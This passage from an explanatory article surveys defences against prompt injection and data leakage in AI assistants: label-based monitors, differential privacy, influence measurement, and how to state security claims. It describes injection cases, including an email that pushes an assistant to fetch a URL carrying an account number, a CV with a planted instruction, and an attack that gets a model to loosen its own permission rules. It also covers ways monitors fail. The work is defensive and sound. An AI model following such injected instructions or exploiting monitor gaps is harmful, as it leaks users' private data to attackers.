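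Some of this loss comes from the models, and better ones should reduce it. GPT-4o sometimes confused FIDES's variable names or opened untrusted data that it didn't need. FIDES completed 68% of travel tasks with o1, a stronger reasoning model, and 41% with GPT-4o.

A better model can't complete tasks that the policy forbids. Many banking tasks ask the agent to read a file and act on it, and FIDES blocks these because the file is untrusted. In SPA's tests on the original benchmark, the label check rejected about 53% of plans, usually because they passed untrusted data to a tool that required more trustworthy data. The checks lowered SPA's task completion rate by 24 percentage points on that benchmark and prevented four successful attacks in 949 runs. That is a poor tradeoff against those attacks, but an attacker who targets SPA specifically might succeed more often without the checks.

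The underlying difficulty is that joining labels can only make them more restrictive. Variables and separate conversations delay this by keeping data away from the main model. Labelling each field separately also helps, because one untrusted field then doesn't change the labels on the others. But if untrusted data has to determine an action, somebody must either endorse the data or give up the task.

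Randori completed more runs when the model could endorse data. With Qwen3.7-plus, it completed 36 of 48 runs with endorsement and 30 without. With MiMo-v2.5, it completed 31 with endorsement and 26 without. No attack on either model succeeded in either case. However, the test has only 16 different tasks, and each completion rate is uncertain by about 20 percentage points either way, so the benefit could be much larger or smaller.

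The comparison with CaMeL is also uncertain because Randori enforces only some of CaMeL's policies, so its higher completion rate may partly reflect looser rules.

Asking Alice to approve each blocked action would also recover some tasks. Costa and colleagues warn that frequent requests lead to *confirmation fatigue*, in which users approve actions without reading them.

### Several agents

Dongol leaves multi-agent systems out of scope. LLMbda covers some of them, because its theorem applies to every program in the language, including programs that run several models in separate conversations. The interpreter tracks the labels of everything that passes between them.

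The guarantee doesn't extend to agents that other people run. Suppose Alice's assistant sends her travel dates to an airline's booking agent. The airline's software may ignore any label on the message, so the policy has to treat the dates as released to the airline. Alice's assistant should also treat the airline's reply as untrusted.

Small permitted leaks can add up too. If each of ten agents is allowed to reveal one bit by finishing or failing, someone who watches all ten could learn ten bits. A claim about the whole system therefore needs its own limit on total leakage.

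## What can be guaranteed about the model itself

The guarantees in the last section hold however the model behaves, but they require trusted code to treat every output as if it depended on everything the model read. A guarantee about the model itself could loosen that requirement, but it has to specify which data it protects, because the model might reveal either its training data or its current context. If a developer trained a model on Alice's old emails, a stranger who has never had access to her inbox might get her account number out of it. If the number is only in today's context, the training method doesn't protect it, because even a model that has memorised nothing can repeat its prompt.

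### Leaving data out, or keeping it apart

The simplest and strongest guarantee about training data comes from leaving the secret out of it. If the training data doesn't depend on Alice's account number, the model's *weights* (the numbers that training adjusts) are the same whatever that number is, so they can't reveal it. This is noninterference, with the training process as the program, and establishing it doesn't require a theory of what the model has learned. Excluding Alice's emails may not be enough, because her account number might also be in a stolen database posted on the web, or in conversations that the developer later uses for further training.

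Excluding private data makes the model worse at tasks the data would help with. *Information Flow Control in Machine Learning through Modular Model Architecture* (Tiwari, Gururangan and colleagues, 2023) describes a company that wants a model to suggest code to its engineers, who can each read only some of its repositories. A model trained on all the repositories could show engineers code they aren't allowed to see. Training a separate model for every combination of permissions would prevent this, but 20 repositories have 2²⁰ combinations, more than a million.

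Tiwari and colleagues instead train one small module, called an *expert*, for each repository. When an engineer makes a request, a *gating function* picks the most relevant experts from those the engineer may use, and the system combines them. Let *D* and *D*′ be two sets of training data that agree on every repository in the engineer's access policy *a*. The guarantee is that for every request *x*,

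$$\mathcal{M}_D(a, x) = \mathcal{M}_{D'}(a, x),$$

where each side is the whole distribution of outputs. The definition also forbids the protected data to influence when the output ends.

Models built from experts usually learn the gating function from all the training data, so the choice between two permitted experts could reveal something about a forbidden repository even if that repository's expert never ran. Tiwari and colleagues therefore restrict the gating and combining steps to information from repositories the engineer may read.

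They tested the design on Reddit posts and public code, with simulated permissions. They measured *perplexity*, which is lower when a model predicts text better. Compared with training on public data alone, the design improved perplexity by 38% on the posts and by 44% to 62% on the code, and it added at most 1.9% to the response time. The design suits a company with dozens of projects better than a service with millions of users, each of whom would need an expert. It can't correct a mistake in the partition. If a colleague pastes Alice's account number into a repository that everyone can read, that repository's expert might reveal it to everyone.

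*Permit* (2026) instead enforces permissions by intervening in a model's internal representations while it generates text. Its measured leakage ranged from 0.0% to 2.5%, and even the 0.0% is only an estimate for the prompts tested. In Tiwari and colleagues' system, leakage is zero for every prompt because the forbidden data is never used to compute the answer.

### Differential privacy

*Differential privacy*, which Dwork and colleagues introduced in 2006, allows every record into the training data but limits how much any one of them can change the result. Training has to be random, so that a given dataset leads to a distribution of possible models rather than to a single one. Let *M*(*D*) be the model that results from training on *D*. Training is (ε, δ)-differentially private if, for every two datasets *D* and *D*′ that differ in one record and every set *S* of possible models,

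$$\Pr[M(D) \in S] \le e^{\varepsilon}\,\Pr[M(D') \in S] + \delta.$$

If ε and δ are both zero, the record makes no difference, which is probabilistic noninterference for that record. Larger values permit more influence. With ε = 2, including a record can make any outcome at most e² ≈ 7.4 times as likely, apart from δ. If an attacker thinks there is a 50% chance that one of Alice's emails was in the training data, examining the model can raise that to at most 88%, again ignoring δ. The limit covers everything anyone could work out from the finished model, including from its reply to any prompt.

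Each time the usual training method updates the weights, it first shrinks any single record's contribution that exceeds a fixed size, then adds enough random noise to hide a contribution of that size.

Google used this method to train VaultGemma, a model with one billion parameters. *VaultGemma* (Sinha, Mesnard and colleagues, 2025) describes it as the largest open model trained with differential privacy from the start. Its privacy guarantee has ε ≤ 2 and δ ≤ 1.1 × 10⁻¹⁰. Many developers apply differential privacy only to *fine-tuning*, the further training of an existing model on new data, which protects the new data but not what the model memorised earlier. VaultGemma's guarantee covers only its original training data, so it doesn't protect Alice's emails if someone later fine-tunes the model on them without differential privacy.

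The strength of a guarantee of ε = 2 depends on what counts as one record. For VaultGemma, a record is a sequence of 1,024 tokens, which is enough for a typical email. But Google's process could sample a document up to seven times, and the guarantee treats the copies as separate records. The permitted ε grows in proportion to the number of records that contain the secret, so for seven copies it is 14, and the factor e^ε rises from 7.4 to about 1.2 million. If Alice's account number appears in dozens of emails, she has almost no guaranteed protection.

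VaultGemma's δ is 1.1 × 10⁻¹⁰, and its 13 trillion training tokens fill roughly 13 billion sequences. An algorithm that published each sequence in full with probability δ would satisfy the definition of differential privacy and publish one or two sequences on average. VaultGemma's training adds noise and doesn't publish sequences this way, but the values of ε and δ alone don't rule it out.

### The cost in quality

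Sinha and colleagues say that VaultGemma is about as useful as non-private models from five years earlier. Ramesh, Pruthi and colleagues (2026), in *The Privacy-Hallucination Tradeoff in Differentially Private Language Models*, tested how often VaultGemma gets facts right. They gave each model the titles of Wikipedia articles on science, had it write the articles, and used another model to check each claim against the original. The last row of the table shows their results, and the other rows come from Google's own tests.

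| Test | VaultGemma 1B | Gemma 3 1B | GPT-2 1.5B |
|---|---|---|---|
| ARC-E (school science questions) | 51.8% | 71.3% | 51.1% |
| HellaSwag (choosing how a passage continues) | 39.1% | 61.0% | 47.9% |
| TriviaQA (general knowledge) | 11.2% | 39.8% | 6.0% |
| Claims supported by the original science article | 39.5% | 50.4% | 39.1% |

Gemma 3 is a newer design, so privacy may not explain the whole difference. But Gemma 2 2B, which was trained on the same data as VaultGemma and has about twice as many parameters, scored 50.3% on the science articles. GPT-2 did as well as VaultGemma on them, although Wikipedia published the articles after GPT-2's release.

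A second experiment by Ramesh and colleagues suggests why. They made up facts about fictional places and trained GPT-2 on them, repeating some more often than others. Without noise, the model learned facts that appeared once in each of 15 passes through the data. With ε = 30, a fact had to appear 60 times per pass, or 900 times in all. With ε of 13 or less, the model learned none of them. The experiment was small, with five facts at each frequency, but the result fits the definition of differential privacy, which limits the influence of rare records whatever they contain. It therefore suppresses the date of an obscure treaty along with Alice's account number. The private models also wrote false statements in place of the facts they hadn't learned.

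### Auditing the privacy parameter

A proof of differential privacy gives an upper bound on ε, and an attack gives a lower bound. To get the lower bound, a tester trains many models with a certain record and many without it. An attack then examines each model and guesses whether the record was in its training data. Let *S* be the set of models for which the attack guesses "yes". The definition limits how much more often a model can fall into *S* when the record was there, so

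$$\text{true positive rate} \le e^{\varepsilon} \times \text{false positive rate} + \delta.$$

Suppose the attack recognises 20% of the models trained with the record and wrongly flags 1% of the others. Ignoring δ and sampling error, e^ε must be at least 20, so ε is at least ln 20 ≈ 3.0. A developer's claim that ε = 2 would therefore be false, since an attack with 1% false positives could then have at most 7.4% true positives. Either the proof is wrong or the software doesn't do what the proof assumes, for example because it samples records differently or adds too little noise.

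Sampling error weakens this conclusion. If the tester trained 1,000 models of each kind, the 95% confidence intervals extend down to 17.6% for the true positive rate and up to 1.8% for the false positive rate, so the tester can claim only that ε is at least about 2.3. With 100 models of each kind and the same observed rates, the lower bound on ε falls to about 0.8, which is compatible with the developer's claim. Training thousands of large models is expensive, so this kind of audit suits small ones.

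An attack that does no better than chance gives a lower bound of zero on ε, so it doesn't show that ε is small. Sinha and colleagues gave VaultGemma the first 50 tokens of about a million training passages and checked whether it continued with the next 50. They found no memorised passages, exact or approximate, while every non-private Gemma model in the comparison had memorised some. This is reassuring but doesn't establish that ε ≤ 2. That guarantee depends on the proof and on correct software.

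### Which inputs influenced an output

None of this protects the model's current context. Several researchers have tried to determine which inputs mattered to a reply, so that the reply carries only those inputs' labels rather than the labels of everything the model read.

The proposal that Costa and colleagues mention, to regenerate a response from the influential messages alone, comes from *Permissive Information-Flow Analysis for Large Language Models* (Siddiqui, Gaonkar and colleagues, 2024). One version of the method finds influential documents through the prompt, and the other uses a model that predicts words from similar stored examples. In tests with an AI agent, the method produced a more permissive label in over 85% of cases than a baseline that asked the model to label its own output. That figure measures how many restrictions the method removed and is not a bound on how much information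 gets out. Regenerating the response keeps the text of the discarded documents out of it, but if a secret determined which documents the search discarded, the choice can still reveal something about the secret.

Štorek, Holzer and colleagues (2026), in *GIF*, do prove a bound. A language model first turns each token into a list of numbers, called an *embedding*. GIF adds a little random noise *U* to the embeddings of one part of the prompt, such as Alice's email, and asks how many bits the next token *Y* reveals about that noise. If τ is the variance of the noise, the theorem says that

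$$I(U; Y) \le \tfrac{1}{2}\log\det(I + \tau M) + o(\tau).$$

Here *I*(*U*; *Y*) is the information that *Y* carries about *U*, and the *I* inside the determinant is the identity matrix. The matrix *M* describes how strongly noise in each direction changes the model's probabilities for the next token. The last term is an error that shrinks faster than τ.

The theorem holds for small noise around one fixed prompt, if the model responds smoothly there. It doesn't give the size of the error at any particular τ. More importantly, it doesn't cover the comparison that noninterference requires. Changing Alice's account number from 48213907 to 48213908 replaces one token with another, and the new embedding may be far from the old one.

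Calculating *M* in full would be too slow, so GIF estimates the size of the effect from a few random probes. It then ranks the tokens by influence and can pass the ranking to a second model, which decides whether the flow breaks the policy. In one example, a job applicant's CV contains an injected instruction to recommend the applicant at a salary of $200,000. GIF attributed 82 bits of influence to the injection and 27 to the employer's real criteria. Štorek and colleagues report that the ranking caught nearly all the injections and privacy leaks in their benchmarks. GIF is therefore a good detector, but it does not prove that the inputs it ranks low had no influence.

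*Sightline* (Xu, Li et al., 2026) proves that an influential input can have a score close to zero. Suppose an email makes the model answer "yes" rather than "no". Let *u* be 1 for this email and −1 for one with the opposite meaning, and let the probability of "yes" be 1/(1 + e^(−20*u*)). Reversing the email's meaning reverses the answer. But at *u* = 1 the model is so certain that a tiny change to *u* has almost no effect, and the influence score is only 0.0000008. GIF's theorem still holds, because it concerns only tiny changes, but a low score is poor evidence that an email is harmless. Confident answers are common. For about one in five outputs of Qwen3-8B, all other tokens together had a probability below 1%.

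Removing an input to see whether the output changes can also mislead. If Alice's account number appears in two emails, removing just one of them may not change the reply, even though the reply contains the number.

Xu and colleagues offer a different kind of guarantee with a tool called Sightline, which measures the model's *attention* to each input, meaning how heavily the model weights that input when computing the output. A classifier trained on labelled examples then scores how likely it is that the output used the input. The tool sets its threshold using inputs known to have influenced an output, one from each of many software projects. Suppose there are 999 such inputs and the threshold is the tenth-lowest score. If a new input that influenced an output resembles these, its score is equally likely to take any of the 1,000 places in the ranking, so it falls below the threshold at most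 1% of the time.

On new projects, Sightline missed about 1% of true influences, as intended, and cleared 44% to 66% of the inputs that had no influence. The 1% is a proved bound on the average over cases drawn in the same way as the calibration data, so it doesn't cover an email that an attacker writes specifically to get a low score. The missed 1% could also include the cases that matter most, such as those involving account numbers.

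### Limiting the influence of a secret in the context

These methods measure influence after the model has answered. Thareja, Nakov and colleagues (2025), in *DP-Fusion*, restrict it while the model is answering. Their software runs the model twice for each new token, once with the sensitive words in the context and once with placeholders instead. It then draws the token from a mixture of the two distributions,

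$$p = \lambda\, p_{\text{private}} + (1-\lambda)\, p_{\text{public}},$$

where λ is as large as possible while the mixture stays within a fixed distance of the public distribution.

Suppose the next token is a digit. Without Alice's account number, the model gives each digit a 10% chance. With the number in its context, it gives "4" a 91% chance and the other digits 1% each. At the loosest setting tested, with no other secrets in the text, λ is about 0.12, so the mixture gives "4" a chance of about 20%.

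The result is a differential privacy bound on the whole output, and it holds even if an attacker chooses the question. The bound is weak because every token adds to ε. For outputs of up to 900 tokens, Thareja and colleagues report average values of ε between 16 and 66, with δ = 0.001. With ε = 16, an attacker's chance of guessing Alice's account number could rise from 1 in 100 million to about 9%. With ε = 66, the formula sets no useful limit on that chance.

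The attacks tested against DP-Fusion succeeded much less often than its proven bound allows. The attacker had to pick the right secret from five candidates after reading a paraphrase of a court document. One standard attack was right 63% of the time when the model paraphrased the original document and 26% to 29% of the time with DP-Fusion, compared with 20% for random guessing. The true leakage lies somewhere in the wide range between what these attacks achieved and what the bound allows.

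Deleting the sensitive words before the model saw the document did about as well. The same attack was right 28% of the time, and the text had similar quality by the paper's main measure. Deletion also gives a stronger guarantee, since words the model never receives can't influence its output. The attacker still beats chance because the surrounding text contains hints, which neither guarantee covers. Both methods depend on finding every sensitive word. In one test, an off-the-shelf tool missed 3.9% of them.

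*ScoreShield* (2026), a later system, applies differential privacy to document retrieval by adding noise to the scores that measure how similar stored texts are to a question. In one set of tests with the model Gemma 3 12B, retrieval without privacy gave 55% accuracy, against a baseline of 46%. With ε between 1 and 10, accuracy fell to about 40%, which is below the baseline. With ε = 100, it recovered to between 52% and 55%, but the privacy guarantee at that value rules out almost no leaks.

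### The dispute over trained refusal

Developers also train models to refuse malicious instructions, but researchers disagree about how much protection this gives. Bhattarai and Vu (2026) write in *Trustworthy Agentic AI Requires Deterministic Architectural Boundaries* that "probabilistic compliance is not security". Like David C of the National Cyber Security Centre, they argue that a model has no built-in boundary between instructions and data. They add that an attacker can imitate even the markers that show who wrote what. Any rule that a model learns for telling instructions from data therefore depends on content that an attacker can forge.

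Bhattarai and Vu state this as a theorem. If nothing outside the model verifies where text came from, some email will make the model treat data as an instruction "with non-zero probability". The theorem is weaker than it sounds, because it holds even if the chance is one in a trillion. As Štorek and colleagues note, a model that samples its words gives every possible next token some probability, so it could produce a forbidden request even after reading an innocent newsletter. The theorem shows that training alone can't reduce the chance to zero, but not that attacks will be practical.

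The case for training is that it reduces expected harm. If strangers send a thousand malicious emails to people like Alice, an assistant that obeys 5% of them causes 50 leaks, and one that obeys 0.2% causes two. Bhattarai and Vu accept that training can reduce attack success rates, but they object to treating a measured rate as a security boundary, because attackers adapt.

A guarantee can be probabilistic, although their slogan implies that probability is the problem. Differential privacy is one example. Its inequality holds for every pair of datasets within its scope and every possible outcome, and the defender's software draws the random noise, so an attacker can't choose it. A measured refusal rate, by contrast, is an average over the attacks that somebody tried. A proof that no email had more than a 0.2% chance of causing a leak, whatever came before it, would also be a guarantee. An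 attacker who sent 100 emails would then have at most a 20% chance of causing a leak. Alice might find that risk unacceptable, but she would know the limit. Conversely, a filter that blocks a fixed list of phrases is deterministic but guarantees nothing about an email that uses other words.

DP-Fusion shows that a probabilistic defence can also limit prompt injection. If the software treats a stranger's email as the sensitive text, the bound limits how much the email can change the model's output. In Thareja and colleagues' tests, a poisoned document succeeded at least 90% of the time against undefended models and never succeeded at the three DP-Fusion settings they highlight. But the defence works only because trusted software identifies which words came from the stranger, and Bhattarai and Vu are right that this information has to come from outside the model.

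Their own architecture also relies on training for some protection. It blocks actions that the policy forbids, but they acknowledge that it can't prevent harm through actions the policy allows. If the policy lets Alice's assistant send her account number to her bank, no monitor will stop the assistant from including it in a message that doesn't need it. Only the model's judgement can prevent that, and at present the most anyone can do is measure how often it does.

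## Writing the claim and judging it

A developer may have a proof about the monitor in Alice's assistant and a measured rate for its model, and these support different kinds of claim. To show readers which kind they are reading, the developer has to state the system and its version, the boundary, the policy, the adversary, the property, the kind of evidence, the assumptions, the exclusions, and the changes that would void the claim.

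### A claim for the fenced assistant

Dongol's Fenced Summariser adds a fence to Alice's email-summarising assistant. Its monitor first allows two tools, the inbox and fetch, and withdraws fetch when it allows the first read of an email. The assistant can still do its job, because summarising an email never requires a fetch.

A complete claim for this assistant might look like this, with invented version numbers.

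| Part of the claim | Alice's assistant |
|---|---|
| System and version | assistant 4.2 with monitor settings 17, and any language model that has no tools of its own |
| Boundary | the plan and the code that runs it, the monitor, the two tools, and Alice's app |
| Policy | the email's author may learn nothing about the account number from web requests |
| Adversary | writes any email, chooses how the model responds to it, and sees the content and order of requests to a web server |
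| Property | once the assistant has read an email, no fetch goes out until the session ends |
| Evidence | a proof about the monitor's rules, and tests that the software follows them |
| Assumptions | the plan contains no fetch; every fetch and every email read goes through the monitor; the inbox has an untrusted label; the monitor withdraws the fetch tool before the model receives the email, and nothing restores it during the session; every session starts empty; outsiders can't see denials; the app loads nothing from outside |
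| Exclusions | emails that Alice pastes into the chat, timing, packet size, and the accuracy of the summary |
| Changes that void it | a new tool, a log that outsiders can read, a retry loop, memory between sessions, or new monitor settings |

The property is a trace property, so a single fetch after an email read would refute it. It also requires weaker assumptions about the model than the fence theorem, which doesn't cover a model that reacts to the monitor's refusals. This property holds even if the model tries again after every denial, because the monitor denies each new attempt.

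The property alone doesn't establish the policy. An assistant that looked up the account number, fetched a page whose address contained the number and only then read the email would satisfy the property and still leak. This can't happen if, as assumed, the plan contains no fetch. The author's server then receives no requests in any run, so its owner sees the same thing whatever the account number is.

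### Three sentences about the same product

Suppose the developer is choosing a sentence for the product's security page.

The claim "The model does not leak data" is too vague to judge. If the model follows the malicious email's instructions every time and requests a fetch with all eight digits in the address, but the monitor denies every request, we can't decide whether that counts as a leak because the claim doesn't specify an observer. It also doesn't specify whether "data" means the emails the model was trained on or the number in its current context.

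Seeing no leaks in 300 tests can, under the right conditions, support an upper bound of about 1% on the leak rate. But runs in which the model never requested a fetch are no evidence that the control restricting fetches works, because the result would have been the same without it. To test that control, a tester should replace the model with a script that requests a fetch at every step.

"No fetch can carry the account number after an untrusted email is read, assuming the following" is a much better claim. It covers every email and everything the model might output, and readers know what would refute it. Its value depends on the assumptions listed. If one were "the model ignores instructions in emails", the claim would be nearly worthless, because whether the model does so is what's in doubt. A person should be able to check every assumption without predicting what the model will do.

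The developer should write "no fetch goes out", because the fence supports this stronger wording, which also rules out leaks through the choice of page.

### The seL4 proof

*seL4* (Murray, Matichuk and colleagues, 2013) makes one of the strongest published claims of this kind. It describes a proof about a microkernel, the small core of an operating system that controls which programs can use which memory and exchange messages. A developer divides the software into partitions and states which partition may send information to which. The theorem is that the kernel's 8,830 lines of C code permit no other flows, under stated assumptions. In the threat model, all software outside the kernel is malicious and works together, and it knows all the code and the whole configuration, but not the contents of other partitions.

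Murray and colleagues first proved a form of noninterference for a simpler description of the kernel. They then extended the result to the C code by using an earlier proof that the code does only what the description allows. Code that meets the description can still leak a secret if it uses the secret to settle a choice the description leaves open, so they had to remove every open choice whose result a program could observe. This work took about 23 of the project's 51 person-months, which don't include the roughly 25 person-years spent on the earlier proof.

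Some of the assumptions came from steps the researchers couldn't prove at first. For example, the kernel deletes an object when the last reference to it disappears, so a partition that gives up its reference might detect whether another partition still holds one. The researchers now require whoever sets up the system to keep a spare copy of each such reference where no partition can delete it. They also require that devices don't write directly to memory, and that programs check devices for new data instead of receiving interrupts.

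The claim excludes timing channels, and Murray and colleagues acknowledge that some exist. For example, a partition can overrun its time slot by calling the kernel just before the slot ends. Programs can also affect one another's speed through shared caches.

seL4's *What the Proofs Assume*, the project's public list, shows how such a claim changes over time. The 2013 proof trusted the compiler, which turns C into machine code. On some processors, an automatic tool now checks the compiler's output, so the proof no longer needs that assumption. The list also includes the assumption that the hardware model captures every relevant channel, followed by the admission "We know this not to be the case." The guarantee therefore covers only the channels in the model.

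Murray and colleagues give three reasons why published security proofs have failed: the reasoning was wrong, the assumptions were unrealistic, or the property was weaker than people thought. Checking a proof by computer makes errors in reasoning very unlikely, but people still have to compare the assumptions with the system in use. For AI assistants, this comparison can fail in several ways.

### Code that differs from the proved model

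Dongol's monitor handles one request at a time, but real agent software may run several tool calls at once. If the software passes an email to the model just before the monitor withdraws the fetch tool, a quick fetch request can get through. The fault shows up as a fetch just after an email read, perhaps only once in thousands of runs.

To look for such differences, a tester can write the monitor's rules as a short separate program and compare its decisions with those of the real software. Three operations (read an email, request a fetch, start a new session) form only 3⁸ = 6,561 sequences of eight, so the tester can try them all. The tester should then repeat the sequences with overlapping requests and deliberate delays, though no finite set of tests covers every possible timing.

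### Wrong labels at the source

The assistant loses access to the fetch tool when it reads an untrusted source. If Alice pastes the malicious email into the chat, the assistant hasn't read an untrusted source, so the tool stays available. The planner may even include the malicious fetch in its plan because it treats the email as part of her request. When this fault occurs, the context contains a stranger's text but the monitor's log shows no untrusted read. A tester can find it by pasting a known malicious email and checking whether the fetch tool is still available. Narisetty and colleagues predict that deployments will fail at the step of deciding which text came from whom, which they found under-specified in every system they surveyed.

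Developers can also forget to label a tool. Microsoft's toolkit for building agents, Agent Framework, now includes FIDES as an experimental feature. According to Microsoft's *Stop prompt injection from hijacking your agent* (2026), the software treats an unlabelled tool as trusted and public. Microsoft's documentation instead lists the default label for such a tool's results as untrusted and public. According to another part of the documentation, the results take the combined label of the tool's inputs, which could make an email trusted if a trusted request opened it. A developer can check which label applies by calling an unlabelled test tool in the version that will ship.

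The untrusted default fails closed for integrity but not for confidentiality, though the documentation describes it as failing "closed rather than open". If the developer forgets to label the tool that looks up Alice's account number, the number counts as public, and a confidentiality check will let it go to any website. The audit log won't reveal the mistake, because it records only calls that the policy blocked or held for approval. The developer can catch it by preventing the assistant from starting if any tool lacks an explicit label, and by sending a canary through each source to see which label it arrives with.

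An explicit label can be wrong too. Microsoft's *Information-flow control* describes a labeling scheme for GitHub that marks files and issues from private repositories as "private" and "trusted". If an employee copies a customer's bug report into a private repository, the customer's text gets the label "trusted". A reviewer should list everyone whose text can end up in each trusted source, not just the people with permission to write there.

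### Tools outside the monitor

Microsoft has also worked with GitHub on experimental label checks for Copilot CLI, a coding assistant that runs in a terminal. So far, the checks cover only selected tools from GitHub's own server. An information-flow claim about such an assistant has to list the tools that the claim covers.

A tester should compare the network's records with the monitor's log, because requests from an unmonitored tool appear only in the network's records. It is safer to let only the monitor open outgoing connections, because an unmonitored tool then stops working instead of leaking data.

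Settings can have the same effect as a missing monitor. Agent Framework has a list of tools that may run even after the agent has read untrusted text, and Microsoft's documentation recommends it for tools that fetch data. Alice's fetch tool also sends an address out, so putting it on this list would remove her protection. Another setting lets users approve calls that the policy would otherwise block. A dry-run mode tracks labels but blocks nothing. It helps developers see which harmless tasks a policy would stop, but the system stays unprotected if somebody forgets to turn enforcement on. Before each release, a script should request a forbidden fetch and confirm that the monitor denies it.

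### Policies that a model writes

In a defence called Progent, ordinary code checks each tool call against a list of rules, but a language model writes the rules and can update them after reading tool results. An attacker may therefore be able to manipulate the model into permitting the attack.

Narisetty and colleagues tested this with Qwen2.5-7B, a small open model, as both the agent and the author of the rules. Their new attack presented the malicious action as a harmless step that the user had already authorised. Averaged over three kinds of task, other attacks succeeded 25.8% of the time without Progent and 4.2% with it. The new attack did no better, at 2.6%. For one kind of task, no attack succeeded even without a defence. Without it, the averages are about 39%, 6% and 4%.

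This is weak evidence that model-written rules are safe. The researchers tried only one hand-written attack, and they suspect that its polite wording made the agent less likely to obey. They work for a company that builds agent-security tools, and the study has not been peer-reviewed. The code that checks the rules is deterministic, but even the ordinary attacks sometimes succeeded, so the result is a measured rate rather than a guarantee.

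The warning sign is a rule that becomes more permissive after the assistant reads untrusted text. A developer can log every change to the rules and test whether malicious emails loosen them. Allowing only changes that make the rules stricter is better. The study used Progent's default setting, which doesn't impose this restriction.

### Changes that void the evidence

Leak rates measured on one model version are no longer valid for the next, because the new model may respond differently to the same emails. A proof that covers every possible output still holds. But if the new version can search the web from the provider's own servers, the system has a new tool, and its searches don't pass through Alice's monitor.

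| Change | Measured leak rate | Claim for the fenced assistant |
|---|---|---|
| A new model version without tools of its own | void | still holds |
| New wording in the developer's instructions | void | still holds if the plan contains no fetch |
| Different emails, or attackers who adapt | void | still holds |
| A new tool | void | void until the developer extends the fence and the proof to it |
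| A log of denied requests that outsiders can read | void if the test didn't count the log as an output | void |
| A retry loop | void | void |
| A new data source, label or exemption | void | void until somebody checks the assumptions again |

The theorem about the monitor still holds when the log is readable, since the monitor still denies the fetch. But the denied address contains Alice's account number, and the email's author can now read it in the log. A retry loop can invalidate the claim because each new attempt starts with the fetch tool available. If the loop passes on an error message from the last attempt, that message may include the email's instruction.

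After fixing a demonstrated leak, the developer can't assume that the new version leaks, or that it doesn't, without testing it.

### The strongest sentence for each kind of evidence

| Evidence | Strongest sentence it supports |
|---|---|
| One run without a leak | "In this run, the server received no request containing the number." |
| One leak of a random canary, confirmed in the server's log | "This version can leak the account number to the email's author." |
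| A significant difference in a paired test | "There is strong statistical evidence that the account number affects what the author sees." |
| 300 independent runs without a leak | "With 95% confidence, at most about 1% of runs under these conditions leak the number in this way." |
| A failed attack by people who knew the defence | "These attackers did not succeed in this many attempts." |
| A proof about a model of the monitor | "No email can cause a fetch after the assistant reads it, if the software matches the model and the listed assumptions hold." |
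| A proof about the code that runs | "No email can cause a fetch after the assistant reads it, if the listed assumptions hold." |
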